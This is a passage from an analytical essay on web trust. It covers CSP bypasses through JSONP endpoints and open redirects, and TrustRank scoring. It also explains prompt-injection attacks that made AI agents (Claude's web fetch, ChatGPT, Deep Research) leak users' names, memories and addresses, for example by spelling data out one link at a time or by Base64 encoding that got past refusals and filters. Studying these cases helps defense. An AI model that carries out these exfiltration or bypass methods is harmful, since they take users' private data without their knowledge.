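In *CSP Is Dead, Long Live CSP!* (2016), Weichselbaum, Spagnuolo and colleagues, all at Google, checked how well such policies worked. They searched an index of about 106 billion pages and found policies on roughly 1.7 million hosts. Because many hosts shared the same policy, the researchers counted each distinct policy once. They called a policy bypassable if an attacker who could inject text into the page could still run a script.

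| Policies | Number | Bypassable | List at least one unsafe host |
|---|---|---|---|
| All distinct policies | 26,011 | 94.72% | 75.81% |
| Enforced policies that restrict scripts | 22,425 | 94.68% | 79.17% |
| Those with no obviously unsafe settings | 2,437 | 51.05% | 41.65% |

The figure of nearly 95% is weaker evidence against host lists than it appears, because 87.63% of policies in the second group allowed scripts written directly into the page, which removes the protection whatever hosts are listed. The last row is a fairer test. Some of the failures in that row depended on Flash, which browsers have since dropped, but most came from unsafe hosts. The researchers considered their counts a lower bound because their automated search looked for only some of the known bypasses.

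Most of the unsafe hosts were reputable sites. Some sites return data as a script and let the requester choose the function that receives it. For example, a request for `events.example/list?callback=show` returns a script that begins with `show`. If an attacker replaces `show` with other code, the approved host sends that code back and the browser runs it. Weichselbaum and colleagues found 194,908 domains with this feature. They also found 101,330 domains, some of them the same ones, that hosted AngularJS, a programming library that can run instructions it finds in a page's text. An attacker could load AngularJS from an approved host even if the page under attack did not use it.

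Of the 15 hosts that appeared most often in policies, 14 had an unsafe feature, though two of these mattered only if the policy also allowed text to run as code. The median policy listed 12 hosts, and the researchers could bypass 94.8% of policies of that length. The features do no harm on their own, so the hosts' owners, who may never have heard of CSP, have little reason to remove them. Open redirectors likewise become dangerous when someone else's rule relies on the host.

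### Why the path stops counting after a redirect

One improvement is to approve a single file instead of a whole host, which CSP has allowed since its second version. Suppose the library approves everything on its own site but only `cdn.example/calendar.js` on a host it shares with strangers. The browser will block a direct request for `cdn.example/other.js`. But if the library has an open redirector, an attacker can request `https://library.example/leave?to=https://cdn.example/other.js`, and `other.js` will load. This works because the first address is on the library's own site, and after a redirect the browser checks only the host, not the path.

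A redirect to `attacker.example` would still fail, because that host isn't in the policy. Browsers therefore check the final destination, which a carelessly written harness doesn't, but they check it less precisely than the original URL.

W3C says this gap is deliberate and protects privacy. The security researcher Egor Homakov had shown that a malicious page could use its own policy to learn about other sites. Suppose `social.example/me` redirects every signed-in user to their own profile. A malicious page could approve only `social.example/me` and `social.example/anna`, then try to load the first as an image. If the browser still checked the path after a redirect, it would block the image for everyone except Anna. The page could detect the block and identify its visitor by trying one name after another.

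Homakov disliked the remedy and, during a debate about removing paths altogether, wrote that "killing paths is killing point of CSP". Homakov wanted browsers to hide whether they had blocked something instead. West (2014), an editor of the standard, replied that neither GitHub nor Facebook used paths in their policies and that no service using them came to mind. The standard kept paths, but browsers ignore them after redirects. Weichselbaum and colleagues concluded that sites can't rely on paths for security because complex sites often have redirectors, sometimes for good reasons such as hiding the address of the page a visitor came from.

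### Letting trusted scripts load others

Weichselbaum and colleagues recommended approving individual scripts instead of hosts. Each time the server sends a page, it picks a new random number, called a nonce, and puts it in the policy and on every script tag the site's developers wrote. The browser runs only scripts whose tags carry that number. An attacker can't guess the number, so a tag they inject won't have it.

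But scripts often load other scripts, and a library written by somebody else won't have the number. The researchers therefore proposed a setting called `strict-dynamic`, which lets a script that the browser has approved load others from any host. Those scripts may load more in turn, and the browser ignores the list of hosts.

This has the same structure as a link-following rule. The scripts with a nonce are the seeds, and each later set adds whatever the scripts in the previous one load. It differs in what counts as a link from one script to another. In W3C's example, an approved script creates a script element in code that points to a file on an unlisted host, and the browser loads the file. When the same script writes a script tag into the page as text, the browser blocks it. Attackers can often get text into a page, but they can't create an element in code unless they are already running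 a script.

Google tried both approaches on Google Maps Activities, which had four million users a month. During 2015, its developers made five major changes to the list of approved sources. The list grew to 15 long paths, at least one of which still let attackers in. After switching to nonces and `strict-dynamic`, the developers had not needed to change the policy again by the time the paper appeared.

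Passing trust along like this works when trusted code determines the next step. Suppose the library's calendar script always loads `https://cdn.example/dates.js`. The library trusted the programmer who wrote the calendar, and that programmer picked the second file. But if the calendar instead loads whatever address appears in the page's URL, as in `library.example/events?plugin=`, an attacker can make it a confused deputy by sending people a link with a hostile address after `plugin=`. The browser will run the attacker's file because a trusted script loaded it.

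Weichselbaum and colleagues acknowledged that `strict-dynamic` makes this mistake more dangerous, since a list of hosts would at least have limited where the file could come from. They still expected nonces to stop a large majority of cross-site scripting attacks, based on a review of hundreds of bugs at Google. They were recommending their own proposal, but W3C now includes it in a set of rules that W3C describes as effective. W3C also advises developers to do without `strict-dynamic` where they can and to check that attackers can't influence which scripts their code loads.

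A web agent is more like the faulty calendar than the sound one, because the text of the pages it reads influences which link it follows. The calendar's programmer can set an address in advance that no text on the page will change.

Even a fixed choice can become unsafe if an attacker changes where an address leads. Web pages often use short addresses such as `/good.js`, which the browser completes with the name of the current site. An attacker who can inject a `base` tag can make the browser complete them with `attacker.example` instead, and the script tag still has its valid nonce. Domains can also change owners. In *Complex Security Policy*, Roth, Barron and colleagues used the Internet Archive to trace the policies of 10,000 popular sites over time, and found that attackers could get past seemingly secure lists through expired or mistyped domains. A chain of trusted scripts has the same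 weakness, because whoever registers an expired domain can answer requests for the files that used to be there.

W3C offers a stricter option for these cases. A site can approve a script by its hash, a fingerprint computed from the file's contents, and the browser will refuse any file that doesn't match, wherever it came from. The site has to update the hash whenever the file changes. That is manageable for a script but useless for a pottery teacher's fees page, which the agent needs to read because the fees may have changed.

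## TrustRank: passing trust along links in web search

With `strict-dynamic`, the tenth script in a chain has the same privileges as the first. Trust can instead weaken at each link, and *Combating Web Spam with TrustRank* (Gyöngyi, Garcia-Molina and Pedersen, 2004) describes a way to do this for the whole web. The method starts from a small set of sites that a person has checked, then follows links to find others that are probably good.

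TrustRank is a method for catching web spam, meaning pages built to trick a search engine into ranking them too high. PageRank, Google's original ranking algorithm, rates a page as important if important pages link to it. It also gives every page a small starting score, so a spammer could raise a page's rank by creating thousands of worthless pages that link to it. TrustRank gives a starting score only to pages that have been checked and judged trustworthy, so spam pages that get links only from each other have no score to pass on.

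### Good pages seldom link to bad ones

TrustRank relies on what Gyöngyi and colleagues call approximate isolation, the observation that good pages seldom link to bad ones. This is because people who write useful pages have little reason to link to spam. Spam pages often link to good ones, though, so trust can pass only from a page to the pages it links to.

The researchers give two exceptions. Spammers can post links on an unmoderated message board, so the board links to spam although its owner never chose to. They can also build a "honey pot", which offers something useful, such as copies of Unix documentation, along with hidden links to spam. Other sites link to the documentation in good faith, and their trust passes through it to the spam.

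### How trust weakens

Gyöngyi and colleagues first considered a link-following rule with a hop limit, which gave full trust to every page within a fixed number of links of a good seed. They tried it on an imaginary web of seven pages, in which one good page linked to a spam page. A limit of two hops gave full trust to all the good pages and no bad ones, but a limit of three gave the spam page the same full score as the seeds.

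TrustRank weakens trust in two ways as it passes along links. Dampening multiplies it by a fixed fraction at each link. If the fraction is 0.85, a page one link from a seed page gets 0.85 of the seed's trust, and a page two links away gets about 0.72. Splitting divides a page's trust equally among the pages it links to, on the theory that people choose links less carefully when they add hundreds of them. A page that receives trust from several others adds the shares together.

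TrustRank combines the two in one formula:

t = αTt + (1 − α)d

- t is the list of trust scores, one for each page.
- T is a table of links. Its entry for row p and column q is 1/ω(q) if page q links to page p, where ω(q) is the number of pages that q links to. Otherwise the entry is 0. This does the splitting.
- α is the dampening fraction, which the researchers set at 0.85.
- d is the list of starting scores. If there are k good seeds, each has 1/k and every other page has 0.

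For a single page p, the formula adds up t(q)/ω(q) for every page q that links to p, multiplies the sum by α, and adds (1 − α)d(p). Because t appears on both sides, a computer starts with t = d and applies the formula repeatedly. The researchers used 20 rounds.

### Five pages by hand

Suppose the library's page on evening classes is the only seed. It links to a pottery teacher's page and to the town's message board. The teacher's page links to the message board and to a clay supplier. The message board links to the supplier and, because a spammer has posted there, to a fake shop. The supplier and the shop link to nothing.

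| Page | Calculation | Score |
|---|---|---|
| Library | 0.15 × 1 | 0.150 |
| Teacher | 0.85 × (0.150 / 2) | 0.064 |
| Message board | 0.85 × (0.150 / 2 + 0.064 / 2) | 0.091 |
| Clay supplier | 0.85 × (0.064 / 2 + 0.091 / 2) | 0.066 |
| Fake shop | 0.85 × (0.091 / 2) | 0.039 |

The supplier and the fake shop are both two hops from the library, so no hop limit can separate them, but TrustRank can because the teacher links only to the supplier. A cutoff of 0.05 would include the four honest pages and exclude the shop.

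Suppose the spammer also links to the shop in the comments on the teacher's page. The supplier and the shop then have links from the same pages, and both score 0.053. The shop passes the cutoff, and no other cutoff would separate it from the supplier.

Errors of this kind also appeared in the researchers' seven-page example. A spam page scored 0.13 because a seed linked directly to it, while one good page scored 0.12 and another, which no page linked to, scored 0.

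### The AltaVista experiment

Gyöngyi and colleagues tested the method on all the pages that the AltaVista search engine had indexed by August 2003. To save computing time, they grouped several billion pages into 31,003,946 sites and scored those.

The researchers found candidate seeds by running PageRank with the links reversed, which favours sites that lead to many others. The top 25,000 candidates included a lot of spam because spammers had copied the entire Open Directory, a large catalogue of links. The researchers dropped every site that no major web directory listed, which left about 7,900. Gyöngyi, who had watched search companies' experts at work, then checked the top 1,250 by hand, and only 178 became seeds. A seed had to be free of spam and have an identifiable owner, such as a university or a government body, that controlled its content.

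To evaluate TrustRank, the researchers sorted all the sites by PageRank and cut the list into 20 groups, each with 5% of the total PageRank. The first group had 86 sites and the last had 5 million. The researchers drew 50 sites from each group and could classify 748 of the 1,000, 613 as good and 135 as spam. They then sorted the sites by TrustRank into groups of the same sizes.

The top five TrustRank groups contained virtually no spam. Under PageRank, almost 20% of the second group was spam, as was half of the ninth and tenth. TrustRank did less well further down, where 31% of its eleventh group was spam. It could not rank the 13 million sites that no other site linked to, since they all scored zero.

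One person judged both the seeds and the sample, which the researchers admit could have biased the results. They also left out 22 sites that hosted personal pages, because each had too many writers for either "good" or "bad" to fit. A harness that scored whole sites would have to accept or refuse each site like these.

The paper also reports results for a cutoff after the tenth group. Of the sample sites above it, 86% were good, compared with 82% of the whole sample, and 55% of all the good sites were above it. By these figures, the cutoff would admit about 55 of the 135 spam sites and exclude about 275 good sites.

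### Ranking errors and authorization errors

These are good results for a search engine, whose quality depends on its average performance over many searches. If the seventh result is spam, the user clicks on another one. Search engines still make such errors. *SafeSearch* (Dong, Guo and colleagues, 2025) found that 380 of 8,933 top-ranked results (4.3%) came from content farms or similar sites.

A harness instead uses a score to permit or refuse each address, and wrongly permitting a single one may be enough for an attack. If an agent opened ten sites at random from those above the tenth-group cutoff, where 14% were spam, it would have about a 78% chance of opening at least one spam site. Pages that attack agents are presumably much rarer than spam was in 2003, but their creators also try to steer agents towards them.

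Opening a bad page doesn't always do harm. Dong and colleagues gave agents harmless questions and added one fabricated, unreliable page to five real search results. The page led to the harmful answer it was designed to produce in 90.5% of trials with GPT-4.1-mini in a simple setup, but in only 4.6% with Claude Sonnet 4.5, which could run further searches. When the researchers forced GPT-4.1-mini to run nine searches instead of three, the rate fell from 50% to 37%, probably because it had more reliable pages to compare with the bad one.

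But that test measured only the agent's final answer. If a page gets the agent to send the user's data to an attacker, the attacker still has the data even if the agent reads eight honest pages afterwards.

Newer models resist such instructions much better. The Decoder's *Opus 5 may have solved browser based prompt injection* reports that attacks on Claude Opus 5 failed in all 129 of Anthropic's browser scenarios, and that attackers succeeded 2.0% of the time in a separate test that allowed them 15 attempts. Even if the 129 scenarios were a fair sample of real attacks, a true success rate of about 2% could still produce no successes among them. Attackers are also more likely to succeed if they can keep trying. According to VentureBeat, an attack through a graphical interface on the earlier Claude Opus 4.6, without safeguards, worked 17.8% of the time on the first attempt and 78.6% by the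 200th.

Even a perfectly accurate TrustRank score would not measure permission to act. A real bank's transfer page would deserve a very high score, but a forged transfer works by sending a request to that same page. A site's score also stays the same when a model appends the user's email address to one of the site's URLs. A private document that a colleague has shared with the user would score zero because no public pages link to it, although the user may want the agent to open it.

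*Causality Laundering* (2026) defines trust in a way that suits permission better than TrustRank does. Before an agent uses a tool, the system looks up all the data that influenced the request and takes the lowest trust level among them. TrustRank adds up the trust passed along links, so enough links from good pages can make up for a bad one. If an agent has read the library's page, the supplier's and the fake shop's, taking the minimum gives it only the fake shop's level of trust when it tries to place an order. However, this means one untrusted page can block a lot of legitimate work.

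### What a cutoff would gain

A score could still be useful if it kept agents away from most bad pages. *The Attack and Defense Landscape of Agentic AI* (2026), a survey, recommends that web agents replace manually maintained domain lists with automated reputation scores, partly because domains expire.

TrustRank with a cutoff has one advantage over a hop limit, because it limits how many addresses an attacker can get permitted with one suitable page. A page can pass on at most 85% of its own score, however many links it contains. If the fake shop published 26 links to spell out the user's surname, each would receive about 0.001, far below the cutoff of 0.05. Whatever the cutoff, the attacker's page would need a score about 31 times as high to lift all 26 links above it without help from other pages.

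This protection works only if the harness scores individual pages. If it scores whole sites, as the AltaVista experiment did, a site that passes the cutoff can offer any number of addresses. But scoring individual pages means refusing everything published since the last calculation, and links change quickly. *CrediBench* (Kondrup, Yang and colleagues, 2025) compared three monthly maps of the web from late 2024, each with more than 45 million domains, and found that only 19% of all the links appeared in all three.

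They also trained a model only on the pattern of links, and it could tell reliable domains from unreliable ones, which were mostly phishing sites, about 69% of the time. Always giving the same answer would have been right 53% of the time. Adding the text of the pages raised the model's accuracy to about 84%. Links are therefore useful as one signal among several, but a 31% error rate is far too high for a rule that grants permission by itself.

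It also matters whether the model or the harness applies the trust score. *GraphRAG under Fire* (2025) tested systems that answer questions from a collection of documents, some planted by an attacker. Scoring the trustworthiness of sources, with clean sources given the maximum score, cut the attack's success rate on one set of questions from 89.2% to 45.7%. This defense relied on the model to give low-scoring documents the right weight, but a harness could have refused those documents outright.

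### Link scores in recent agent research

Several recent proposals reuse TrustRank's mathematics to help users or agents choose which other agents to work with. *The Trust Fabric* (2025) uses almost the same formula, but replaces pages with agents and links with one agent's trust in another. Seliuchenko's *TrustFlow* (2026) gives each agent a separate reputation for each kind of work. In a test with 50 agents, groups that colluded to raise their own scores reduced the accuracy of the top recommendations by at most four percentage points. Both systems produce rankings, and users or agents can correct a poor recommendation by choosing a different agent next time.

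*AuthRank* (Jia, Ramesh and colleagues, 2025), which scores reports about cyberattacks, is the closest method to TrustRank for agents that read documents. The researchers found that these reports rarely link to each other, and that a link may exist only because one report disputes another. They therefore had a language model judge whether each report continued the discussion in an earlier one, and ran PageRank on the connections it found. An agent can then check a report's score at each step of its research. On a standard set of questions with false documents mixed in, the scores improved accuracy by about 10–15% in most cases.

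In one demonstration, an attacker published a blog post calling a domain harmless, then used the domain to spread malware. The system repeated the blog post's claim when it ran without the scores, but answered that it did not know when it had them.

An honest first report from an unknown author also gets a low score, and Jia and colleagues did not measure how often this would hide a real warning. They also assumed that the attacker did not know about the scores and would not try to raise them, for example by impersonating a respected author. They propose, as one remedy for later work, letting authority flow only from a small set of verified authors, which would give AuthRank hand-checked seeds like those TrustRank had in 2004.

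## Claude's web fetch tool and the July 2026 data leak

Anthropic's rule for Claude used no scores and did not limit hops. It lasted about ten months in the Claude chat app. In July 2026, the developer Ayush Paul showed that a website could use the rule to get a user's name, employer and home city out of Claude, and Anthropic stopped the app from following links.

### The rule of September 2025

Anthropic released the web fetch tool to developers in September 2025. Claude asks for a web page or PDF, Anthropic's servers retrieve it, and the text goes into the conversation. Anthropic limited the tool to addresses that had already appeared in the conversation, and listed the places that counted:

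- the user's messages
- the results of tools that run on the developer's side, such as a program that reads the user's email
- the results of earlier web searches and web fetches

A URL that Claude made up did not count, and neither did one in the output of a program that Claude had run on Anthropic's servers. The second exclusion was necessary because a program can join pieces of text. Without it, Claude could have run one line of code that printed an attacker's URL with the user's email address on the end, and that URL would have counted because it was in the conversation.

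The ban on composed addresses blocks the standard exfiltration attack. Willison tested the same tool in the Claude app and found that it also rejected addresses Claude had composed.

The last item on the list, fetch results, let Claude follow links from one page to the next, because each fetch result included the addresses on the fetched page. If the list had ended at search results, Claude could have opened only the seeds.

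Anthropic also blocks the developer tool from opening addresses longer than 250 characters. It blocks addresses on private networks too, so a hostile link can't send the tool to a machine behind a company's firewall. The tool follows robots.txt, a site's file listing what automated visitors may open, but this doesn't hinder an attacker who writes the file for their own site. The tool has no default cap on the number of fetches.

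Anthropic warned developers that some risk remained and advised them to use the tool only in trusted environments or with non-sensitive data. Anthropic did not follow this advice in its own chat app, which combined the tool with memories of the user's past conversations.

### How Paul got the data out

Paul explains in *The Memory Heist* (2026) that Claude's memory then had two parts. A summary of recent conversations, updated daily, went into every new conversation, and a search tool let Claude look through the full history. Claude therefore had access to its user's name and employer even when the user asked only about a coffee shop.

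Paul first asked Claude to open an address on Paul's server that ended with Paul's name. The harness refused, as the rule required. Paul then put up a home page with a link for each letter and asked Claude to choose the link for the first letter of the name. The server logged a request for `/a`.

Next, Paul had the server generate a new page of letter links after each choice, with a hyphen as the 27th link. After loading the home page, Claude spelled out "ayush-paul" in ten requests. Each address repeated the letters already chosen, so the last request contained the whole name.

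In these trials Claude was doing what its user had asked. A real attack had to get Claude to do the same thing without the user's knowledge, which took more work. Simple injected instructions were unreliable, and Claude was suspicious of a made-up loyalty scheme. The attack that worked used a coffee shop's website behind a fake security check. The check imitated Cloudflare, a company that protects many websites from unwanted traffic, and told AI assistants to identify their users before entering. Claude spelled out the user's name, employer and home city, while the conversation still looked harmless to the user.

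A user who inspected the link first would have seen only the coffee shop. Web software normally identifies itself with a short text called a user agent, and the one sent by Claude's fetcher includes the name "Claude-User". Willison (2026) reports in *How I tricked Claude into leaking your deepest, darkest secrets* that Paul's server showed the fake check only to visitors with that name. Identifying the fetcher is good practice because it lets site owners block it, but it also lets an attacker show Claude a page that no person will see.

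Claude had to infer one of the three answers, the home city of Charlotte. *The Read-Only Lie*, אִם יִרְצֶה הַשֵּׁם's blog post about the leak, notes that Paul had never told Claude the city. Claude worked it out from the name of a high school hackathon. A user can't reliably prevent such inferences by deleting facts from Claude's memory, and a filter that searched outgoing requests for stored facts would have missed the city even if Claude had sent it in one piece.

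Tencent Zhuque Lab's *Why AI Agent's Memory Becomes Attacker's Data Goldmine* (2026) describes a reproduction of the attack with a different target, an API key (a password that one program uses to access another). Each of the lab's pages had 37 links, one for each letter and digit and one for the hyphen, and the test agent leaked the key one character at a time. The test is weak evidence about how easily a page can fool a well-trained model, because the lab had told its agent to follow instructions on web pages and complete any verification steps. It does show that the method works on other agents that follow links and can reach a secret.

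### How much a choice of link reveals

A choice among b equally likely links reveals log₂ b bits, which is 4.70 bits for 26 links, 4.75 for Paul's 27 and 5.21 for Zhuque Lab's 37.

After k choices, Claude can have reached any of bᵏ addresses. To identify one of N equally likely secrets, an attacker therefore needs enough choices to make bᵏ at least N:

k ≥ log₂ N / log₂ b

There are 26¹², or about 9.5 × 10¹⁶, strings of 12 letters, so identifying one takes 56.4 bits. Each fetch picks one of 26 letters, which conveys 4.70 bits, so the full string takes 12 fetches after the one that opens the first page.

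The attacker can reduce the number of fetches by putting more links on each page. If a page has a link for every pair of letters, 676 in all, each fetch reveals two letters. Doubling the number of links adds only one bit to each choice, so halving the number of fetches requires squaring the number of links. Claude also has to read all those links. The last column of the table estimates the total for the whole name in tokens, the short pieces of text that models process. The estimate assumes 30 characters per link and four characters per token, the ratio in Anthropic's examples.

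| Links on each page | Bits per choice | Fetches for a 12-letter name | Tokens Claude must read |
|---|---|---|---|
| 2 | 1.00 | 57 | 900 |
| 26 (single letters) | 4.70 | 12 | 2,300 |
| 676 (pairs) | 9.40 | 6 | 30,000 |
| 17,576 (groups of three) | 14.10 | 4 | 530,000 |

Pairs of letters seem like the best choice for an attacker who wants to work quickly. A list of three-letter groups would fill half the context window of a model that can hold a million tokens, and a limit of 100,000 tokens per page, as in Anthropic's example settings, would cut the list short.

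A developer can also cap the number of fetches. An example in Anthropic's documentation sets the cap at five, which leaves four choices of link after the first page. Four choices can reveal four letters if each page has 26 links, or eight letters if each has 676. A cap on fetches is therefore much weaker without a cap on page length.

An attacker can often get a whole word in one fetch by listing the likely answers. A page that lists 500 cities can identify the user's city this way, while spelling "charlotte" takes nine fetches. A random API key has to be spelled out, because no list of likely keys exists. With Zhuque Lab's pages, a 40-character key would take 40 fetches, or about a minute at the one to two seconds the lab saw between requests.

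The formula gives the maximum information that a choice can reveal. If Claude has already spelled "charlott", the attacker learns almost nothing new from the final "e". The number of bits also doesn't measure the harm. With a page of two links, an attacker can learn one bit, such as whether the user is looking for another job, which the user's employer might very much want to know.

אִם יִרְצֶה הַשֵּׁם estimates that Paul's three answers came to about 30 characters, or 143 bits, and so took about 30 fetches to leak. An address that Claude composed itself could have held 200 characters, about 950 bits, in a single request. The rule slowed the leak a great deal and gave Claude some 30 chances to notice that something was wrong, but names and cities are short enough to leak even at that rate.

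The same post calls the links a covert channel, meaning a path that carries information although nobody designed it to. The term goes back to a 1973 paper by the computer scientist Butler Lampson. The post suggests watching for a run of fetches from one site in which each address is a character longer than the last, but notes that ordinary pages in a numbered series can look similar. An attacker could avoid this detector quite easily by having the server give every link a random name of the same length and record which letter each one stood for.

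### Anthropic's response

Paul reported the problem to Anthropic, which paid no bounty, saying it had already found the flaw internally. Anthropic then removed the app's ability to open links from pages the tool had fetched. Hackaday's *This Week In Security* gives the same account of the reply and the fix.

If Anthropic did know, it left link-following on for some time in an app that put users' memories into every conversation. The flaw was foreseeable, because the documentation had listed fetch results as a source of permitted addresses since the tool's release, and anyone who runs a website decides what it links to. Perhaps the company expected Claude to refuse the instructions. Claude did refuse Paul's crudest attempts, but the harness is supposed to protect the user when the model is fooled.

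The day after Paul's post, Anthropic replaced the daily memory summary with separate entries that Claude reads and updates during conversations. The announcement doesn't mention the leak. Separate entries may be easier for users to check, but they would not have stopped Paul's attack, because Claude can still read them while it browses.

### The developer tools still follow links

The fix covered the chat app. Developers who build their own products on Claude use a separate version of the tool. According to its August 2026 documentation, that version could still fetch addresses found in earlier fetch results. Anthropic's *Claude Platform release notes* for July 24 to September 3 list no change to this rule.

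Anthropic included the same permission in a newer rule, so the evidence for it is not limited to an old page of documentation that might be out of date. The rule took effect on October 7 and applies to Claude Managed Agents, a service in which Anthropic runs agents for developers. It lets the service's web fetch tool open only addresses that have already appeared in the session, and it lists pages fetched earlier as one of the places where they may have appeared.

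| Where the address appeared | Claude app, after the fix | Developer tool, August 2026 | Managed Agents, October 2026 |
|---|---|---|---|
| User's message | Permitted | Permitted | Permitted |
| Web search result | Permitted | Permitted | Permitted |
| Page fetched earlier | Refused | Permitted | Permitted |
| Output of the developer's own tools | Refused | Permitted | Refused |
| Only in Claude's own text | Refused | Refused | Refused |

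Anthropic says that the October rule reduces the risk of exfiltration, and it does, because it stops agents in that service from opening addresses they have composed. The rule also excludes addresses from attached documents and most other tools, which makes it harder for a hostile email to supply a starting address. But a site built like Paul's should still work against such an agent if the agent has private information and the page's text can get it to cooperate.

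There is a reasonable case for treating developers differently. They decide what private data their agents hold, and an agent that compares pottery classes for anonymous visitors has no memories to leak. They can cap the number of fetches or name the domains the agent may visit. Since October 20 an administrator can also switch web fetch off for a whole organisation or set one list of domains for everyone. In Managed Agents, an address reached through a redirect must pass that list as well as the agent's own, so an open redirect on an approved site won't take the agent off the list. (Approved sites can themselves leak data, as a separate incident with one of Anthropic's products showed.)

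These measures only help if developers know they need them. A developer who reads that Claude can't construct addresses may conclude that it can't send data out, the mistake Paul exploited. It would be safer to refuse links from fetched pages by default and let developers turn them on for agents without secrets. If an agent suddenly can't open a link, somebody will notice the error, but a leak is easy to miss because the agent still answers normally.

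### What the fix costs

In the library example, Claude in the chat app can still open the page on evening classes and see the addresses of the four fee pages, but it can no longer open those pages. It has to search for each one, and the search may not return the same address. If each search succeeds 90% of the time, Claude will find all four pages only about 66% of the time.

A well-known news article is easy to find this way. Search engines are less likely to have indexed the second page of a long list, a file a town council posted that morning, or a very small business's website. אִם יִרְצֶה הַשֵּׁם also mentions software documentation, which is often spread over many linked pages.

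Checking sources also becomes less reliable. A report's link identifies the exact document it cites, but a search for the title might return a later edition or a newspaper's summary, and Claude could check the claim against the wrong text. The user can paste the address into the chat, but doing this for thirty footnotes is tiresome.

The fix prevents an attack that requires a purpose-built site and either a user who sends Claude there or a search that leads Claude to it. There is no public evidence that criminals have used this attack. I'd be cautious about reading much into that, because the victim's conversation looks normal and the evidence is in the attacker's log.

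אִם יִרְצֶה הַשֵּׁם proposes a compromise: Claude may follow links only on domains the user has named in the conversation. This would restore much of what research lost, since Claude could follow links within the library's site, though not to the teachers' own sites. It would not have stopped Paul's attack, because the user gave Claude the coffee shop's address, so the attacker's domain would have been allowed.

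Another option is to separate the browsing from the memories. One copy of Claude could read the web and follow any link with only the information the task requires, then pass its findings to a second copy that has the memories about the user but can't open pages. A search for pottery classes might need the name of the user's town but not the name of their employer. A site could still extract the town. Separating the two follows Anthropic's advice to developers about sensitive data, but it works least well when the task is private, such as research into the user's illness.

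### What search results still allow

After the fix, the app permits only addresses that come from the user or from web search. Neither source is entirely safe. Users paste in emails and documents without reading every link, and an email could contain 26 links, one for each letter of the alphabet. Claude could then spell out a name by opening the matching links in sequence, without following a link from any fetched page.

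Search results are a more open route, because anyone can publish a page and wait for a search engine to index it. Claude writes its own search queries, and the rule on addresses doesn't restrict them. An attacker can't see the queries but can see which of their own pages Claude opens. They could publish one page for each letter, then try to get Claude to search for the pages and open them in the order that spells out the data. Researchers have already leaked data from ChatGPT one letter at a time through addresses fixed in advance.

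This would be harder than Paul's attack. The server can't generate new pages as each letter arrives, because a search engine has to index them first. Each letter may require a search as well as a fetch, and the right page has to appear in the results. The tool also caches pages, so "Hannah" might appear in the attacker's log as only "h", "a" and "n". Publishing several pages for each letter would avoid this, but the search engine would have to index more pages.

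The attacker could again save effort by listing likely answers. With one indexed page for each of 500 cities, a single fetch would reveal the user's city, and a travel site with a page for every city would look ordinary.

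## ChatGPT's check that an address is already public

OpenAI lets ChatGPT open an address automatically if a crawler with no access to anyone's conversations has already found it on the public web. This rule does not depend on links in the conversation. OpenAI described it in January 2026, nearly three years after researchers first reported that ChatGPT could leak data through addresses. In between, OpenAI tried two other rules, and researchers found ways to leak data under both.

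### Images that carried the conversation

ChatGPT can put a picture in an answer by writing the picture's address in Markdown, a simple notation for formatting text. The user's browser then requests the picture from that address. In 2023 an injected instruction could make ChatGPT summarise the conversation and add the summary to the address of a picture on an attacker's server. Roman Samoilenko found this flaw at the end of March, and Johann Rehberger, the security researcher behind the blog Embrace The Red, found it independently a few days later. In Rehberger's demonstration, in the post *ChatGPT Plugins*, the stolen text included "TooManySecrets123" from earlier in the chat.

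Rehberger reported the flaw to OpenAI and to Microsoft, whose Bing Chat had the same problem. According to Embrace The Red's *Bing Chat*, Microsoft had fixed it by mid-June, and Bing Chat then seemed to load images only from a few of Microsoft's own hosts.

OpenAI did not add a check until December, when its website began sending each image's address to an OpenAI service called `url_safe`, which classified the address as safe or unsafe before the image was displayed. Embrace The Red's *OpenAI Begins Tackling ChatGPT Data Leak Vulnerability* describes quick tests from the day the check appeared. The service rejected an image address with an email address at the end. But when Rehberger tried 36 images, one for each letter and digit, nine loaded, which was enough to spell "hi" in two requests. Rehberger could see no reason why `a.png` passed and `d.png` failed.

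OpenAI did not explain how the service decided. Rehberger guessed that it might look addresses up in Bing's search index, a method close to the rule OpenAI later adopted. The iPhone app did not yet use the check.

### Addresses on trusted domains

Later tests suggested that the service relied heavily on an address's domain. In October 2024 Rehberger reported that it accepted addresses on `blob.core.windows.net`, where Microsoft's cloud customers store files. Embrace The Red's *Exfiltrating Your ChatGPT Chat History and Memories With Prompt Injection* shows ChatGPT sending the user's recent chat history to an address on that domain.

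The security company Tenable found that the service also accepted every address on `bing.com`. Bing's search results link to `bing.com` addresses that redirect to the real sites. Tenable's *OpenAI ChatGPT url_safe Mechanism Bypass* (2025) calls this "essentially an open redirect as a service", since anyone whose site Bing has indexed gets such an address.

Nobody can alter these `bing.com` addresses, so Tenable could not add a secret to one. Tenable's *HackedGPT* describes how the researchers instead had Bing index one page for each letter of the alphabet, then made ChatGPT display images through the links for H, E, L, L and O in turn. Tenable reported the bypass in December 2024, asked OpenAI for updates six times, and published its advisory while the flaw was still unfixed.

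Tenable's work also shows a limit of separating browsing from memories. ChatGPT already used a second model, SearchGPT, to read web pages without access to the user's memories. Tenable planted instructions on a page that made SearchGPT end its report with further instructions for ChatGPT. When the user sent another message, ChatGPT read the report again and followed them. ChatGPT could see the memories and could still cause requests by displaying images. The separation would have prevented this leak only if ChatGPT had been unable to cause requests.

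### ShadowLeak

The `url_safe` service checked addresses in ChatGPT's answers. Deep Research, an agent that OpenAI released in February 2025, opens pages itself while preparing a report. Its requests for these pages come from OpenAI's servers, and the security company Radware found no comparable check on them.

Radware's *ShadowLeak* describes an attack on a user who has connected Deep Research to Gmail. The attacker sends an email with the subject "Restructuring Package – Action Items" and hides instructions in it, for example in white text on a white background. When the user later asks for a report on the day's emails, the agent reads the attacker's email, finds an employee's name and home address in another message, and requests a URL on the attacker's server with those details added to the end. The user sees no sign of the request.

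Radware developed the attack over several attempts. Deep Research refused a plain instruction to send the data. When the email named the tool to use, some requests failed, so the next version told the agent to keep trying. The agent then sometimes opened the address but left off the personal details. The final version told the agent to encode them in Base64 first, supposedly for security, and this worked every time in repeated tests.

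Base64 is a standard way of writing data with letters, digits and a few symbols, and anyone can reverse it. In Base64, "charlotte" becomes `Y2hhcmxvdHRl`. Radware believes the software carrying out the request received only a harmless-looking string. A filter could decode Base64, but the attacker could ask for some other encoding, so refusing all composed addresses is safer.

The request left from OpenAI's servers, so the victim's employer could not have seen it in its own network logs. Radware reported the flaw in June 2025, and OpenAI fixed it in early August.

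### ZombieAgent

OpenAI then limited ChatGPT to opening addresses exactly as it had received them. ChatGPT refused to add anything to an address, even when told to. This restriction resembles Anthropic's ban on composed addresses and has the same weakness.

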